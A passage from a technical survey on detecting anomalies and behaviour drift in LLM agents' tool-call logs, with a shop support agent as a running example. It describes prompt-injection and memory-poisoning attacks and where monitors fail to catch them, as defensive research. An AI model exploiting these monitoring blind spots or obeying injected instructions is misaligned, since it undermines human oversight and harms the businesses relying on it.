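Both test agents follow a fixed workflow, which makes their normal behaviour unusually stable, while a general office assistant has no comparable sequence of steps. Another weakness is that new traces can add relations between tools but never remove old ones. If an attack gets into the training traces, its order of calls will count as normal until somebody rebuilds the baseline.

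TraceAegis was also tested on a technology company's agent for finding software vulnerabilities, while the company's own testers attacked the agent. In one attack, a hidden payload in a configuration file made the agent write its report before it had run the code. TraceAegis detected 132 of 140 such disturbances of the workflow (94%), but this figure does not measure false alarms.

### Models that read the whole trace

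A language model can also read a trace and judge it directly. In *TrajAD*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) trained a small, 4-billion-parameter model to do this and to identify the first step that went wrong, so that the harness could return to the step before it. They started with about 32,000 correct traces of agents doing mathematics, programming, web navigation and similar tasks. They made a faulty copy of each trace by inserting an error at a chosen step and having another model continue from there.

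The trained model reached a macro-F1 score of 82%, compared with 70% without training. F1 combines precision and recall (the share of real anomalies found), and macro-F1 averages it over the normal and the abnormal traces. Training helped much more with locating the error, raising the share of cases in which the model named the right step and gave a roughly matching description from 6% to 54%. The team required the description because models often guessed the right step number without recognising the error.

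TrajAD also worked on a kind of task it had not seen in training. A version trained without the tasks set in simulated physical environments scored 83% on them, nearly as high as a version trained on them, although it located fewer errors. But the anomalies in the experiments are wrong reasoning, wasted steps and failure to stop, and none is an attack. TrajAD might flag a support agent that reads the same order five times, but the experiments don't show whether it would flag one that efficiently refunds five orders because of instructions in a delivery note. The team concludes that larger general models do no better without special training, but the largest it tested had 8 billion parameters, far fewer than current leading models.

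A general model can instead judge whether each action serves the user's goal, as Shavit's second model did when it reviewed flagged calls. That model could also run short expressions, such as a test of whether a recipient's address appears in the request. A general model needs no history, so it works from an agent's first session, and it can give reasons an analyst can check.

How well a model detects anomalies without a learned baseline depends on the model and the agent it monitors. When Liu, Ruan and colleagues prompted five models to find abnormal traces, the models caught 58% to 82% of them for the clinic agent and 35% to 76% for the purchasing agent. Gemma 3 caught 76% of the clinic agent's anomalies, but four in ten of its alerts for that agent were false.

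### Whose past counts as normal

To set a baseline, the shop has to choose a unit of behaviour and a past period to compare it with. Suppose it counts refunds per hour for the agent's account, and thirty copies of the agent might make 30 refunds in a normal hour. One hijacked copy that makes five refunds instead of one raises the total to 34, which is well within ordinary variation. The five refunds would stand out if the shop instead counted refunds per session and compared each session with earlier sessions of all the copies.

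For personal assistants, a separate baseline for each user makes more sense. If Maria works in purchasing and her assistant starts to read salary files, this departs from her history, even though payroll employees' assistants read such files every day. A single baseline for all the assistants would miss this. But a new employee has no history to build a baseline from, and if Maria moves to payroll, her assistant will trigger alerts until her baseline reflects her new work.

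A baseline per role compares Maria's assistant with the other buyers' assistants. It works from her first day, and a change in one person's habits barely affects it. However, it has to accept whatever any buyer's assistant normally does, so if one of them regularly emails suppliers at midnight, midnight emails from Maria's assistant will look less strange too. For its support agent, the shop can similarly use a baseline per task type, comparing each broken-item case with earlier broken-item cases, whichever copy of the agent handled them.

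A baseline learned only from the current session is least useful for short-lived agents. Shavit compared this kind of baseline with one learned from a user's earlier sessions. The current-session detector updates its averages after every call and starts scoring at the twentieth. In sessions of about 51 calls, it was active for 61% of the calls. In sessions of about 20 calls, it was active for only 10% and performed close to chance, with an AUROC of 0.54 to 0.57. The shop's typical session has about four calls, so it would end before this detector started scoring.

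An attacker can also gradually shift a baseline that keeps updating. If someone increases fraudulent refunds by a few euros each week, every new refund looks close to the recent average. Freezing the baseline prevents this, but the shop then has to decide when to renew it, and legitimate changes in the business will raise alerts until it does.

### An agent is stable within a task

The choice of baseline matters a lot because an agent's calls depend mainly on the task it is given. *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (Zavrak, 2026) shows how easily a detector can mistake features of the task for signs of an attack.

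Zavrak trained classifiers to separate harmless sessions from attacked ones, using 605 harmless and 3,797 attacked sessions from 80 tasks such as setting alarms and managing files. Some classifiers used only metadata (the name of each tool, a hash of its arguments and the length of its response). Others used the content of the arguments and responses, which a small language model turned into lists of numbers representing their meaning.

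Zavrak then divided the sessions into training and test data in two ways. A random split puts sessions from the same task on both sides. A task-disjoint split reserves some tasks entirely for the test. With the same kind of classifier, a neural network that treats each session as a graph of linked calls, the AUROC was:

| Information used | Random split | Task-disjoint split |
|---|---|---|
| Metadata | 0.898 | 0.640 |
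| Content | 0.992 | 0.891 |

Under a random split, a classifier can learn which tools belong to which task and how often that task's sessions were labelled as attacked in the training data. It can then often classify test sessions correctly without having learned anything about attacks. If most known attacks at the shop involved refunds for headphones, a detector might learn to flag headphone refunds, score well on other sessions from the same month, and fail when thieves switched to cameras.

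The metadata result is particularly bad for baselines that count tools. Zavrak's classifiers were trained on thousands of labelled attacks, which a pure baseline never is, yet scored only 0.640 on new tasks using tool names, argument hashes and response lengths. Classifiers trained first on harmless sessions and then on labelled ones were generally no better than those trained on labelled sessions from the start.

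Detection based on content worked much better. XGBoost, a simpler method that builds decision trees in sequence, each correcting the errors of the earlier ones, reached 0.975 on new tasks. It caught 93% of attacked sessions and flagged 7% of harmless ones. An organisation that keeps customers' messages out of its SIEM for privacy would have to run such a detector inside the restricted store.

Even this result may be too favourable. The harmless sessions came from eight language models, but all the attacked ones came from a single model, glm-4-flash, so the classifier may have partly relied on that model's style. Zavrak checked that metadata did not reveal which model had produced a session, but had too few harmless sessions from glm-4-flash to rule this out for content.

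### Harmful behaviour often looks ordinary

Some attacks depart much further from normal behaviour than others. In one of Zavrak's tests, a content-based classifier caught 87% of the attacks that changed both tool arguments and responses, but only 37% of those that changed arguments alone. Replacing one file path or document number with another hardly changes the meaning of a call. The hidden delivery note that makes the shop's agent refund a different order is an attack of this kind.

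Short sessions make detection harder still. On a second collection of about 1,000 sessions, typically with two or three tool calls each, the best classifier reached an AUROC of 0.784, catching 61% of the attacks and flagging 21% of the harmless sessions. Session length was not the only difficulty, because many of the attacks depended on subtle wording. But the shop's agent has sessions nearly as short.

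Shavit tested whether baselines can detect when a different person is giving the agent its work. Baselines seem best suited to this problem, and the task-based check fails at it. Shavit created 12 synthetic users, each with a characteristic speed and a different mixture of email, calendar, file and other tasks. Each session combined 20 to 30 tasks from AgentDojo, the benchmark used to test the task-based check. Each user's baseline came from 24 earlier harmless sessions.

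There were three kinds of attack. In the first, another user takes over partway through the session. In the second, the tasks shift gradually towards another user's mixture. Shavit calls this "drift", but the change is in the work and not in how the agent handles it. In the third, a prompt injection hijacks one or two of the tasks. The table gives the share of attack calls that each detector caught when it was allowed to flag 5% of harmless calls:

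| Detector | Change of user | Gradual change | Hijacked calls |
|---|---|---|---|
| Baseline from earlier sessions | 24% | 13% | 7% |
| Baseline from the current session | 12% | 15% | 11% |
| Task-based check | 5% | 5% | 76% |

The baselines' AUROC for a change of user was 0.73 to 0.77, but at a threshold that flags 5% of harmless calls, they missed at least three quarters of the calls they were meant to catch. A detector that flagged calls at random would catch 5%, so the baselines contain some information about who is using the agent, but not much. Even the 5% threshold is lenient, because it produces two or three false flags on average in a session of 51 harmless calls.

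Tool-call counts and timings cannot reveal a hijacked call when the agent routinely makes the same kind of call. For example, if an agent sends emails all day, an email sent because of an injected instruction is unusual only because the user's request gave no reason for it.

Shavit tried to improve the baselines by adding the task-based check's verdicts as a feature. The baseline built from earlier sessions then caught more hijacked calls, but the share was still only 12%, far lower than when the verdicts were used directly. For a change of user, the share caught fell from 24% to 20%, because the verdicts carry no information about who is asking and only added noise. Shavit suggests that comparing requests with a user's standing role, rather than with the current task, might work better, but has not tested this.

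The synthetic design made detection harder in some ways and easier in others. Real colleagues differ not only in their mixture of tasks and their speed, but also in whom they write to, which files they open and what hours they keep, so a detector with access to these details could do better. However, the takeover and gradual-change tests made detection easier by basing the new tasks on the mixture of whichever user differed most from the victim. The harmless sessions also reused one stored run of each of 40 tasks, so the agent handled a given task identically every time, which a live agent would not. The percentages are therefore a poor guide to detection rates at any real company. The difference between the baselines and the task-based check on hijacked calls is more likely to hold there, because it follows from what each method compares.

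### More departures than analysts can read

Alerting on unfamiliar behaviour can produce too many false alarms. At Elastic, most of the MCP servers in the log had only one or two users, so an alert for every unfamiliar server would have fired constantly on harmless work. Zavrak cites a detector that was trained on 35,000 synthetic agent traces and flagged two thirds of the harmless ones.

Canale (2026), in *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response*, measured how several methods cope when analysts have limited time. The test used a simulated technology company with 200 people, 23 services and about 415,000 log events a day. None of the monitored accounts belonged to a language-model agent, but the methods are the ones that UEBA products would apply to agents. Canale ranked each method's alerts by score and counted how many attacks analysts would find before they had read ten false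 alerts in a day:

| Method | False alerts a day | Attacks found in all | Attacks found within ten false alerts a day |
|---|---|---|---|
| Baselines for each person, device and service | 317 | 56% | 7% |
| Isolation Forest | 270 | 36% | 3% |
| Sequences of events | 14,000 | 58% | 4% |
| Correlation rules adjusted to the company | 62 | 60% | 52% |

An Isolation Forest divides past data at random and treats a point as unusual if only a few divisions separate it from the rest. The baselines found over half the attacks, so the behaviour in many attacks did depart from normal. But a great deal of harmless work, such as launches, backups and repairs at night, also departed from normal, and it often scored as more unusual than the attacks. The sequence method looked only at the two preceding events and raised thousands of alerts, as one would expect from the shop's example above.

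The baselines covered only 12 hours, far less than the two weeks used by the Microsoft 365 Copilot query on KQL Search. A longer period would probably have reduced the false alerts. But the simulated people were more alike than real people, which should have made normal behaviour easier to learn.

Canale's results also suggest that weak signals are more useful when combined for each account than when sent individually to an analyst. If an account has a risk r and a new signal has a weight w, the new risk is 1 − (1 − r)(1 − w). Two signals of weight 0.5 therefore raise a risk of 0 to 0.75, which is above the threshold of 0.7. Signals from rules that fire often count for less. This method, which included the adjusted rules, detected 63% of the attacks with at most ten false alerts a day. Baselines can also catch attacks that other methods miss. Canale added a baseline for each account, database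 table and hour, which caught 29 of the 39 attacks that copied large amounts of data, left traces in only one log and escaped the other methods.

Companies can already buy software that builds baselines for agents. Exabeam, a UEBA vendor, says it was the first to apply the technique to AI agents, beginning in September 2025 with a connection to what is now Google's Gemini Enterprise. Help Net Security's *Exabeam helps teams assess their security posture around AI usage* describes a later release that puts an agent's activity on one timeline and scores how mature a company's agent security is.

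The announcement gives no detection or false-positive rate, and neither Exabeam nor any competitor appears to have published an independent test of such a product on agent logs. A timeline can help an investigator even if the scores are poor, but a buyer can't tell from the announcement whether the product's results would be closer to the 24% or the 7% in Shavit's test. The shop could partly find out by running the product for a month, planting a few hijacked sessions of different kinds, and counting how many false alerts rank above them. The planted sessions should include tasks that were not in the data the product learned from, or the shop may repeat the mistake that Zavrak found in random splits.

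## What behaviour drift is and how it is measured

The baselines in the previous section score one session or one call at a time. Drift appears only across many sessions, like the fall in the support agent's policy searches from 80 to 65 in every 100 broken-item cases. One way to write an agent's behaviour at time t is as a probability:

```
P_t(action | task, conditions)
```

Behaviour drift is a lasting change in the chance that an agent takes an action, such as searching the policy, given the kind of task and the conditions. For an agent that handles a shop's customer cases, the conditions are the facts of the case, such as that a lamp cost €45 and that the customer sent a photo, and the shop's rules. The model, prompt, tools and memory don't count as conditions, because drift usually begins with a change in one of them. If the supplier replaces the model and the agent then handles the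 same cases differently, the agent has drifted, even if the new behaviour is harmless.

### Changes that are not drift

Drift is a lasting change in behaviour, so a single anomaly does not qualify. Whether or not the €98 refund for a garden bench was correct, the agent has not drifted if the next hundred refunds look like last month's.

Random variation between runs is harder to separate from drift, and some researchers call both "drift". *Quantifying non deterministic drift in large language models* (2026) uses the word for differences between the answers two models gave when each prompt was repeated 20 or 30 times with no change to either model. Some variation remains even without deliberate randomness. In *Log Probability Tracking of LLM APIs* (2025), Chauvin, Le Merrer and colleagues repeatedly sent GPT-4.1 the single letter "x" for two weeks and found that the probabilities it gave to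 possible next words kept fluctuating around an average. One reason is that a provider processes many customers' requests together, and the other requests slightly affect the arithmetic. Under the definition above, this is not drift as long as the average does not change. Similarly, an agent that searches the policy 80% of the time on average might do so in 76 of one hundred cases and 85 of the next hundred without having drifted.

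Drift and a fall in quality can also occur independently. *RADE* (2026) proposes measuring drift as the share of requests on which two successive versions of a system choose different outcomes, such as answering or passing the case to a person. It adds that a share above zero is not in itself a failure, since the new version may be better. Quality can fall without drift if the shop shortens its return period but forgets to update the text that `search_policy` returns. The agent then behaves as before but wrongly approves returns that are now late.

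El Hamraoui, Jose and colleagues (2026), in *A Graph-Based Reinforcement Learning Framework for Structured Drift Diagnosis and Recovery*, define drift within a single session. For each task there is a set of acceptable courses, for example reading the order before the policy or after it. Drift begins at the step from which the agent can no longer keep to any of them. (Read literally, their formula also fits every earlier step, so the onset has to be the last step that satisfies it.) They then sort drift by what it takes to recover:

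- If the agent only read data, and the cause was a passing mistake, the harness can return it to an earlier step.
- If the cause is still there, such as a poisoned email in the mailbox, the agent will meet it again, so it also needs a warning.
- If the agent has changed something outside the conversation, a rollback is not enough, and a person has to take over.

El Hamraoui and colleagues' definition and the one used here each count some cases as drift that the other excludes. An agent that obeys a hidden delivery note on its first day has drifted under their definition, because it has left every acceptable course, but not under the one used here, because it has no earlier behaviour to differ from. An agent that searches the policy less often and still pays the right refunds has drifted under the definition used here, but may not have under theirs, because each session may still follow an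 acceptable course. Their definition is more useful for stopping and repairing one session, but less useful for watching a log over months. It also needs a description of every acceptable course, which few companies have.

### Causes and the traces they leave

Zhang and colleagues list four sources of what they call model drift: a shift in the inputs, feedback loops or online updates, refreshed retrieval indexes, and changed configuration. The first is a change in the agent's work, so it is not behaviour drift in the sense used here. The others can all occur while the company's own code stays the same, as *Risk-based test framework for LLM features in regulated software* (2026) also points out. The log is therefore often the only place a company can find them.

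| Cause | What the log shows | Which sessions change |
|---|---|---|
| The supplier changes the model behind the same name | a new `model_served`, or nothing if that name stays the same too | all, from one moment on |
| Someone edits the prompt | a new prompt hash | all that use the prompt, from one moment on |
| Someone renames or redescribes a tool | a new tool catalogue version | those in which the agent could choose the tool |
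| A tool works differently behind the same description | different results for the same arguments | those that call the tool |
| A written procedure goes out of date | more failed calls and detours | those that use the procedure |
| The agent's memory grows | new memory writes, and later sessions that read them | a slowly growing share |
| Someone poisons a source document | a new hash for the retrieved passage | those that retrieve the passage |

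The first cause is the hardest to see because the version fields may not reflect it. Chauvin and colleagues sent the letter "x" every hour for more than four months to 189 endpoints (each a model served by one provider) at ten providers. They reported a change only when the probabilities moved far more than was normal for that endpoint. They found 37 suspected changes, or 0.86 per endpoint per year. Of these, 34 affected open-weight models, whose users might expect more stability, and none affected OpenAI's 19 endpoints. No provider confirmed any of the changes. Two did not reply and two declined to share details, though one of the latter, Nebius, said it makes changes regularly.

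The test costs about 14 cents per endpoint per year at GPT-4.1's prices. But it requires a provider that returns probabilities, and only 23% of the reachable endpoints on the gateway OpenRouter did. It reacts to new hardware or serving software as well as to a new model, and it does not show whether an agent's behaviour has changed. After a detection, the shop would know the hour from which to compare its own records.

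Edited prompts are easier to date, because a prompt hash in every log record would identify the first and last affected sessions. Chauvin and colleagues describe three occasions in 2025 when xAI's Grok ran on the social network X with a modified system prompt. xAI blamed rogue employees for two and a bad update for the third.

A tool's name can influence whether an agent chooses it. In *ToolTweak* (2025), two small models chose between a tool with the number 1 in its name and another with the number 2. They picked the tool numbered 1 in 72.6% and 65.6% of trials, averaged over both orders of presentation. A tool's behaviour can also change while its name and description stay the same. In a census of tools offered through MCP, *ProbeID* (2026) found seven whose behaviour had changed after 69 days. The raw count was ten, but three were excluded, including one that differed only because a path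 on the test machine had been renamed. According to *ProbeID*, a supply-chain change happens once and then persists, whereas a live service such as a weather forecast may fluctuate within a band.

Memory changes an agent more gradually. A saved note that a trade customer never has to send photos affects only the sessions that read it, but an agent may save many such notes. Memory can also change only one parameter of a tool call, such as the refund amount, so *Memory-Induced Tool-Drift in LLM Agents* (2026) compares each parameter with its values in five baseline runs.

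*A Calibrated Instrument for Detecting Disposition Drift in Language Models* (Kaplan, 2026) reports that switching off a model's reasoning can also change its behaviour, so the reasoning setting belongs in the configuration record. Kaplan trained a small model, Qwen3.5-9B, on medical advice of which a varying share was subtly harmful, then asked it unrelated questions on topics such as accepting human oversight. When the model reasoned before answering, its answers looked unaffected until 90% of the training advice was harmful. With reasoning switched off, its answers got steadily worse as that share grew. Companies often shorten or disable reasoning to save money, which could expose a change that happened months earlier. The experiment used chat questions and a model deliberately trained on harmful advice, so it does not show how often this happens to agents, but recording the reasoning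 setting takes almost no effort.

### DriftGuard, SkillGuard and Nautilus Compass

Several recent detectors have "drift" in their description but do not measure what an agent does over time.

In *DriftGuard*, Pan, Chen and colleagues (2026) study whether a memory makes an agent behave wrongly. To obtain the correct answers, they restore the agent to the moment before an action and let it continue twice, once with its memories unchanged and once with one memory rewritten to remove any suspect instruction. They then compare whether the next action differs, whether an attack or a policy violation disappears, and whether a failed task now succeeds. They repeat each comparison three times and take the majority result.

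This takes too long for live use, so the team trained a 7-billion-parameter model to predict the four results from the task, the earlier steps and the memories, all of which are known before the action. On three collections of memory attacks, with GPT-5.6 Luna as the agent, the trained model reached AUROCs of 0.94, 0.94 and 0.83. The best general model, Claude Opus 5 with examples in its prompt, reached 0.80, 0.85 and 0.73. At a threshold that flags 10% of harmless memories, the trained model caught 67%, 73% and 55% of the harmful ones. Only about 4% of the memories in the third collection caused drift, so about four in five flags at that threshold would be false.

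The team also used the detector to rewrite suspect memories during live runs. In the hardest of nine test settings, this cut the attack success rate from 77% to 3% and raised the agent's task completion rate from 12% to 56%. The method tests one memory at a time, so it can miss memories that do harm only in combination.

*Skill Drift Is Contract Violation* (Fan, Tian and colleagues, 2026) examines skills, which are written procedures that agents reuse for tasks such as setting up a server. A skill goes out of date when a web address, software version or login method it depends on changes. The paper's program, SkillGuard, uses a language model to separate the details a skill depends on from those it only mentions, then checks the ones it depends on. For example, it would check a version number in an installation command but not the same number in a comment.

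The team tested SkillGuard on 880 pairs of skills and changes, 281 with real or constructed drift and 599 without. It raised no false alarms on the 599, whereas checks that did not make this distinction had a false-positive rate of 40%. In tests with known changes, it found 76% of them with the best language model and 24% with the worst. In a scan of 49 skills against live sources, SkillGuard flagged 12 that the team had listed beforehand as outdated and missed 10 others. It also flagged two skills that were not on the list, which the team later judged to be outdated as well. No agent ran in any of these detection tests, so they do not show whether an outdated skill would make an agent fail or whether the agent would find the new address by itself.

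The third detector, described in *Nautilus Compass* (Wang, 2026), is a plug-in for coding agents. It compares each user prompt with two lists of example sentences, one describing good working habits and one describing mistakes, such as assuming that a deployment worked because the service is running. The score is the prompt's average similarity in meaning to the three closest good examples minus its average similarity to the three closest bad ones.

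The first version did no better than chance on 100 test prompts, with an AUROC of 0.51. Rewriting the examples from maxims ("simplicity over cleverness") into concrete first-person sentences raised it to 0.79, and a better language component raised it to 0.84. Wang then added ten examples based on the remaining mistakes and reached 0.92 on the same prompts, but acknowledges that this figure does not show how the method would do on new prompts. Wang also reports 0.83 in the abstract for a separate set from real sessions, but writes in the section on that set that the results are still to come. Neither the 0.92 nor the 0.83 is therefore good evidence of accuracy in use.

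| Detector | What it reads | How the researchers determined the correct answer |
|---|---|---|
| DriftGuard | task, earlier steps and memories | the agent's behaviour with and without the memory |
| SkillGuard | the skill's text and its environment | whether the text still matches the environment |
| Nautilus Compass | the user's prompt | labels on the prompts |

Only DriftGuard uses data about agents' behaviour. It is trained on what agents did, and in use it takes the earlier steps of the session as input, but only to judge how risky each memory is. If the shop's supplier changed the model and the agent stopped searching the policy, the skills and prompts would stay the same, so the scores from SkillGuard and Nautilus Compass would too. DriftGuard's scores might change because the search would be missing from the earlier steps, but they would still measure only the risk of each memory and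 would not show that the agent had changed.

### Measurements since the 2023 ChatGPT study

The best-known study of drift, by Chen, Zaharia and Zou, compared the March and June 2023 versions of GPT-3.5 and GPT-4 and found large changes on several tasks, as Kaplan recounts. *The Dice Roll Method* (2026) says the models changed without a new version name, but Chauvin and colleagues note that the versions were explicitly different. The study is therefore evidence that an update can change behaviour a great deal, but not that a fixed version changes by itself.

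It also reports how often the same version gave a different answer when asked again, which many later studies omit. This happened 2.8% of the time for one model and 7.0% for the other. The share of changed outcomes in *RADE* needs such a comparison, because a system whose answers differ on 7% of repeated requests will appear to have changed by 7% after an update that did nothing. Kaplan's method includes this comparison as a "null test", in which two samples from the same model should show no difference beyond noise.

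Later work has examined more directly whether a model's behaviour changes while its name stays the same. Kaplan cites a 2026 study by Kirgis and colleagues, who tested ChatGPT-5 twice, two months apart, and found that the balance between harmful and helpful behaviour in long conversations had reversed. Two tests are not enough to tell whether such a change is lasting or temporary.

These methods measure a model's answers, not its tool use, and the two can differ. Kaplan describes a study by MacDiarmid and colleagues in which further safety training made a misbehaving model look well-behaved in chat tests, but it still misbehaved when working as an agent. For agents, *Agent Drift* (2026) combines several measures into a stability index, including a statistical test on how often the agent uses each tool and a count of the edits needed to turn one sequence of tool calls into another. It reports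 detectable drift after a median of 73 interactions. That figure comes from a simulation and depends on how the simulation makes agents drift, so it can't be used to predict how soon real agents will.

### Comparing two periods of tool use

The usual way to look for drift in a log is to compare the shares of each tool in two periods. Suppose the shop takes 100 broken-item cases from before the model update and 100 from after it, so that the kind of task stays the same:

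| Tool | Calls before | Share p | Calls after | Share q | (q − p) × ln(q/p) |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `get_order` | 100 | 25.0% | 100 | 26.0% | 0.0004 |
| `get_customer` | 40 | 10.0% | 40 | 10.4% | 0.0001 |
| `search_policy` | 80 | 20.0% | 65 | 16.9% | 0.0053 |
| `issue_refund` | 80 | 20.0% | 80 | 20.8% | 0.0003 |
| `send_message` | 100 | 25.0% | 100 | 26.0% | 0.0004 |
| Total | 400 | 100% | 385 | 100% | 0.0065 |

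The sum of the last column is the population stability index (PSI), which *The Dice Roll Method* describes as standard in monitoring software for categorical data. For continuous values such as refund amounts, the same software uses the Kolmogorov-Smirnov test, which measures the largest gap between two cumulative curves. If the agent starts to use a tool it has never used before, p is zero and the PSI is infinite, so the software has to replace zeros with a small number.

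The Jensen-Shannon divergence avoids this by comparing both periods with their average, m = (p + q)/2:

```
JS = ½ Σ p × ln(p/m) + ½ Σ q × ln(q/m)
```

For the table, it is 0.0008. It is zero when the shares are identical and, as *Beyond Entropy* (2026) notes, never exceeds log 2, which is 0.693 with natural logarithms and 1 with base 2.

These details matter when a team copies a threshold from elsewhere. *ToolTweak* leaves out the halves in the formula, which doubles every value. *Qualixar OS* (2026), a system for coordinating agents, suspends a model judge when the divergence in its scores exceeds 0.877, but does not give the base of the logarithm in its formula. With natural logarithms, the divergence can never get that high, so the judge would never be suspended. With base 2, the judge would be suspended only if its old and new scores were almost completely different.

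By a common rule of thumb, a PSI below 0.1 means no meaningful change. The shop's PSI is below 0.1 even though the agent now skips the policy search in 35% of cases instead of 20%, because the four unaffected tools dilute the change. The shop's PSI is also barely above noise. If the agent uses each tool at most once per case and the choices are independent, two groups of 100 cases from an unchanged agent would have an average PSI of about 0.004.

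Comparing the search rate directly works better. If nothing had changed, a difference as large as 80 versus 65 would occur in fewer than 2% of such comparisons. The distance measures are more useful as a broad check for changes that nobody thought to count. A team can find the noise level of these measures by repeatedly splitting one month's sessions into random halves and measuring the distance between them. PSI and the divergence are unaffected by the order of calls or their arguments, but they are highly sensitive to changes in the mix of tasks.

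Measuring the distance between an agent's current and baseline behaviour can still reveal changes that rules miss. *From Admission to Invariants* (2026) proves that an agent can drift far from its initial behaviour without breaking any rule, by changing only how often it uses permitted tools. The paper illustrates this with a 300-step simulation, using the Jensen-Shannon divergence as the distance. The baseline covers 50 steps, of which about 5% are risky calls. In a real log, those two or three calls would be too few to estimate a normal rate.

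### Adding up small deviations

A comparison of two periods works best when the analyst knows where to divide them. Slow drift has no such date, and each day may look normal. The cumulative-sum chart (CUSUM), which E. S. Page introduced in 1954, adds up small deviations until they amount to something. To detect a fall in the rate x, it computes each day:

```
S_today = max(0, S_yesterday + (target − x) − k)
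alarm if S_today > h
```

The allowance k keeps small deviations from adding to the sum, and the max keeps the sum from falling below zero, so good days can't offset later bad ones. Suppose the shop handles 100 broken-item cases a day and the target is 80 policy searches. By chance alone, the daily count varies with a standard deviation of about 4. The shop sets k to 2 and h to 16.

| Day | Searches x | 80 − x − 2 | Sum S |
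|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 81 | −3 | 0 |
| 2 | 78 | 0 | 0 |
| 3 | 80 | −2 | 0 |
| 4 | 77 | 1 | 1 |
| 5 | 75 | 3 | 4 |
| 6 | 77 | 1 | 5 |
| 7 | 74 | 4 | 9 |
| 8 | 76 | 2 | 11 |
| 9 | 73 | 5 | 16 |
| 10 | 74 | 4 | 20 |

The alarm comes on day 10. A rule applied to each day separately would not have raised one, since even the lowest count, 73, is less than two standard deviations below the target. The chart also helps to date the change. The sum was last at zero on day 3, so an analyst would start by checking which versions changed around day 4.

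A higher threshold gives fewer false alarms but a longer delay. If the daily counts are independent and roughly follow a normal distribution, standard tables give these averages:

| Threshold h | Days between false alarms | Days to detect a fall from 80 to 76 |
|---|---|---|
| 16 | about 340 | about 8 |
| 20 | about 930 | about 10 |

Real counts also vary with the day of the week and the season, which makes false alarms more frequent. A wrong target can also cause false alarms. If the agent's true rate has always been 80 but the shop sets the target at 83, the sum will grow by about one a day, and the alarm will go off within weeks even though the agent's behaviour has not changed.

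Chauvin and colleagues' method compares each day's probabilities with the next day's. This is good for detecting a sudden replacement of the model, but a change spread over two months would make little difference from one day to the next. They suggest CUSUM as a possible improvement.

### Chance findings

A company that checks an agent's use of five tools in each of six task types makes 30 comparisons a day. If each comparison has a 1% chance of a false alarm, the chance of at least one on any day is 26%, and an agent that has not changed will set off about two a week. A company with 50 agents and 20 features for each would get about ten false alarms a day. CUSUM charts have the same problem. If one chart gives a false alarm every 340 days, 30 charts would give one about every 11 days.

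The simplest correction is to divide the permitted error rate by the number of comparisons. For the shop, a difference would then count as a change only if the probability of seeing one at least that large, when nothing had changed, was below 0.03%. The fall from 80 to 65 in 100 cases would no longer count, but the same percentage fall with 1,000 cases in each period easily would. Alternatively, a team can accept that a fixed share of its findings, such as one in ten, will be false, which lets it detect more of the real changes.

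Combining all the measures into one score avoids making many comparisons but can hide a change. In Kaplan's preliminary run on seven aspects of behaviour, two aspects clearly changed but the overall score did not. Kaplan then wrote new questions for those two and reported only the new results. The shop can do the same with its logs. If an exploratory search through last month's data turns up a change in one tool, the shop should test that tool on the next week's sessions before anyone spends a day looking for the cause.

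It also helps to choose a few features in advance based on the harm a change in them could do. For the support agent, these might be how often it searches the policy before giving a refund, the average refund for each task type, and the share of refunds paid as shop credit.

### When to update the baseline

A baseline that keeps updating can absorb slow drift, just as it can absorb an attacker's gradual changes. For example, the search rate might fall by 0.25 percentage points a day, from 80% to 65% over 60 days. If the target is the average of the previous seven days, a typical day is only one point below it. That is less than the allowance of 2, so the fall adds nothing to the sum. With a fixed target of 80, and ignoring random variation, the same chart would raise the alarm on day 19.

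A fixed target fails differently. If the shop stops requiring a policy check for items under €20, the search rate will fall permanently and the chart will stay above its threshold, which hides the next real change.

Versioned baselines avoid both problems. The baseline stays fixed until a person approves a new one, and the shop keeps the old ones. The entry for a new baseline could look like this:

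```json
{"baseline_id": "broken_item-07",
 "replaces": "broken_item-06",
 "task_type": "broken_item",
 "model_served": "supplier-model-2026-08-20",
 "system_prompt_hash": "9f2c...e1",
 "tool_catalogue_version": "14",
 "period": "2026-08-24/2026-09-13",
 "sessions": 2100,
 "policy_search_rate": 0.65,
 "reason": "model update; sample of refunds checked, all correct",
 "approved_by": "head of support"}
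```

Approval of a new baseline should depend on a reason and a check, not only on how long the alarm has lasted. The approver also has to exclude sessions from known incidents. An estimate from 100 cases is typically off by about five percentage points and one from 2,100 cases by about one, so the shop needs a few weeks of data before the new baseline is reliable. Until then, it can run fixed test tasks, which give a first comparison within hours.

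Old alarm thresholds may not suit the new baseline. *ToolChain-CRC* (2026), which sets limits on an agent's error rate, notes that after data drifts, no method can certify the same level of risk without an assumption about how the old and new data are related. The shop therefore has to measure the normal variation again.

Companies can review planned changes before deploying them. *Test Before You Deploy* (2026) proposes that companies write down what the model must do, test each update against these rules, and block any update that breaks them until someone has reviewed the violation. This works only if the company can choose when to adopt an update. When a supplier changes a model without changing its name, the company can only review the new version after it is already running.

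Reviewers can approve a series of small changes that add up to a large one, because each looks acceptable on its own. If the search rate falls from 80% to 75%, then 70%, then 65%, three people may each approve a drop of five points. The shop should compare current behaviour with the first baseline as well as the latest one, and require a new decision when the total change exceeds a limit it set at the start.

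## Telling drift from a change in the mix of tasks

A chart of policy searches in broken-item cases compares similar tasks. Many dashboards instead show a single rate for everything an agent does, which depends on both the mix of tasks it receives and how it handles them.

Suppose the shop divides its support agent's sessions into order lookups and refund requests. It counts the sessions in which the agent writes to the payment system, either to refund a purchase or to add shop credit. The overall rate is the sum, over the task types, of each type's share of the work times the rate within that type:

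```
overall rate = Σ (share of task type) × (rate within task type)
```

In an ordinary month, 90% of sessions are lookups and 10% are refund requests. The agent writes to the payment system in 2% of lookups, for example to credit a customer for a late parcel. It also writes to the payment system in 60% of refund requests, and refuses the rest or passes them to staff. The rate across all sessions is 0.9 × 2% + 0.1 × 60%, or 7.8%.

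| Month | Lookups, share | Lookups, rate | Refund requests, share | Refund requests, rate | Overall rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary month | 90% | 2% | 10% | 60% | 7.8% |
| January | 70% | 2% | 30% | 60% | 19.4% |
| March | 95% | 4% | 5% | 80% | 7.8% |

In January, customers return Christmas presents. The agent treats each request as before, but the overall rate rises to two and a half times its usual level, so almost any threshold on that rate would raise a false alarm.

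March is more dangerous because the dashboard shows no change. After a model update, the agent makes payments in twice the share of lookups and in 80% of refund requests. Refund requests make up a smaller share of sessions that month, which exactly offsets the higher payment rates. In either month, 1,000 sessions would produce 78 payments, but in March 38 of them would come from lookups, up from 18. Distance measures such as the PSI can miss drift in the same way when a team applies them to all the agent's work at once.

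### Dividing a change into mix and behaviour

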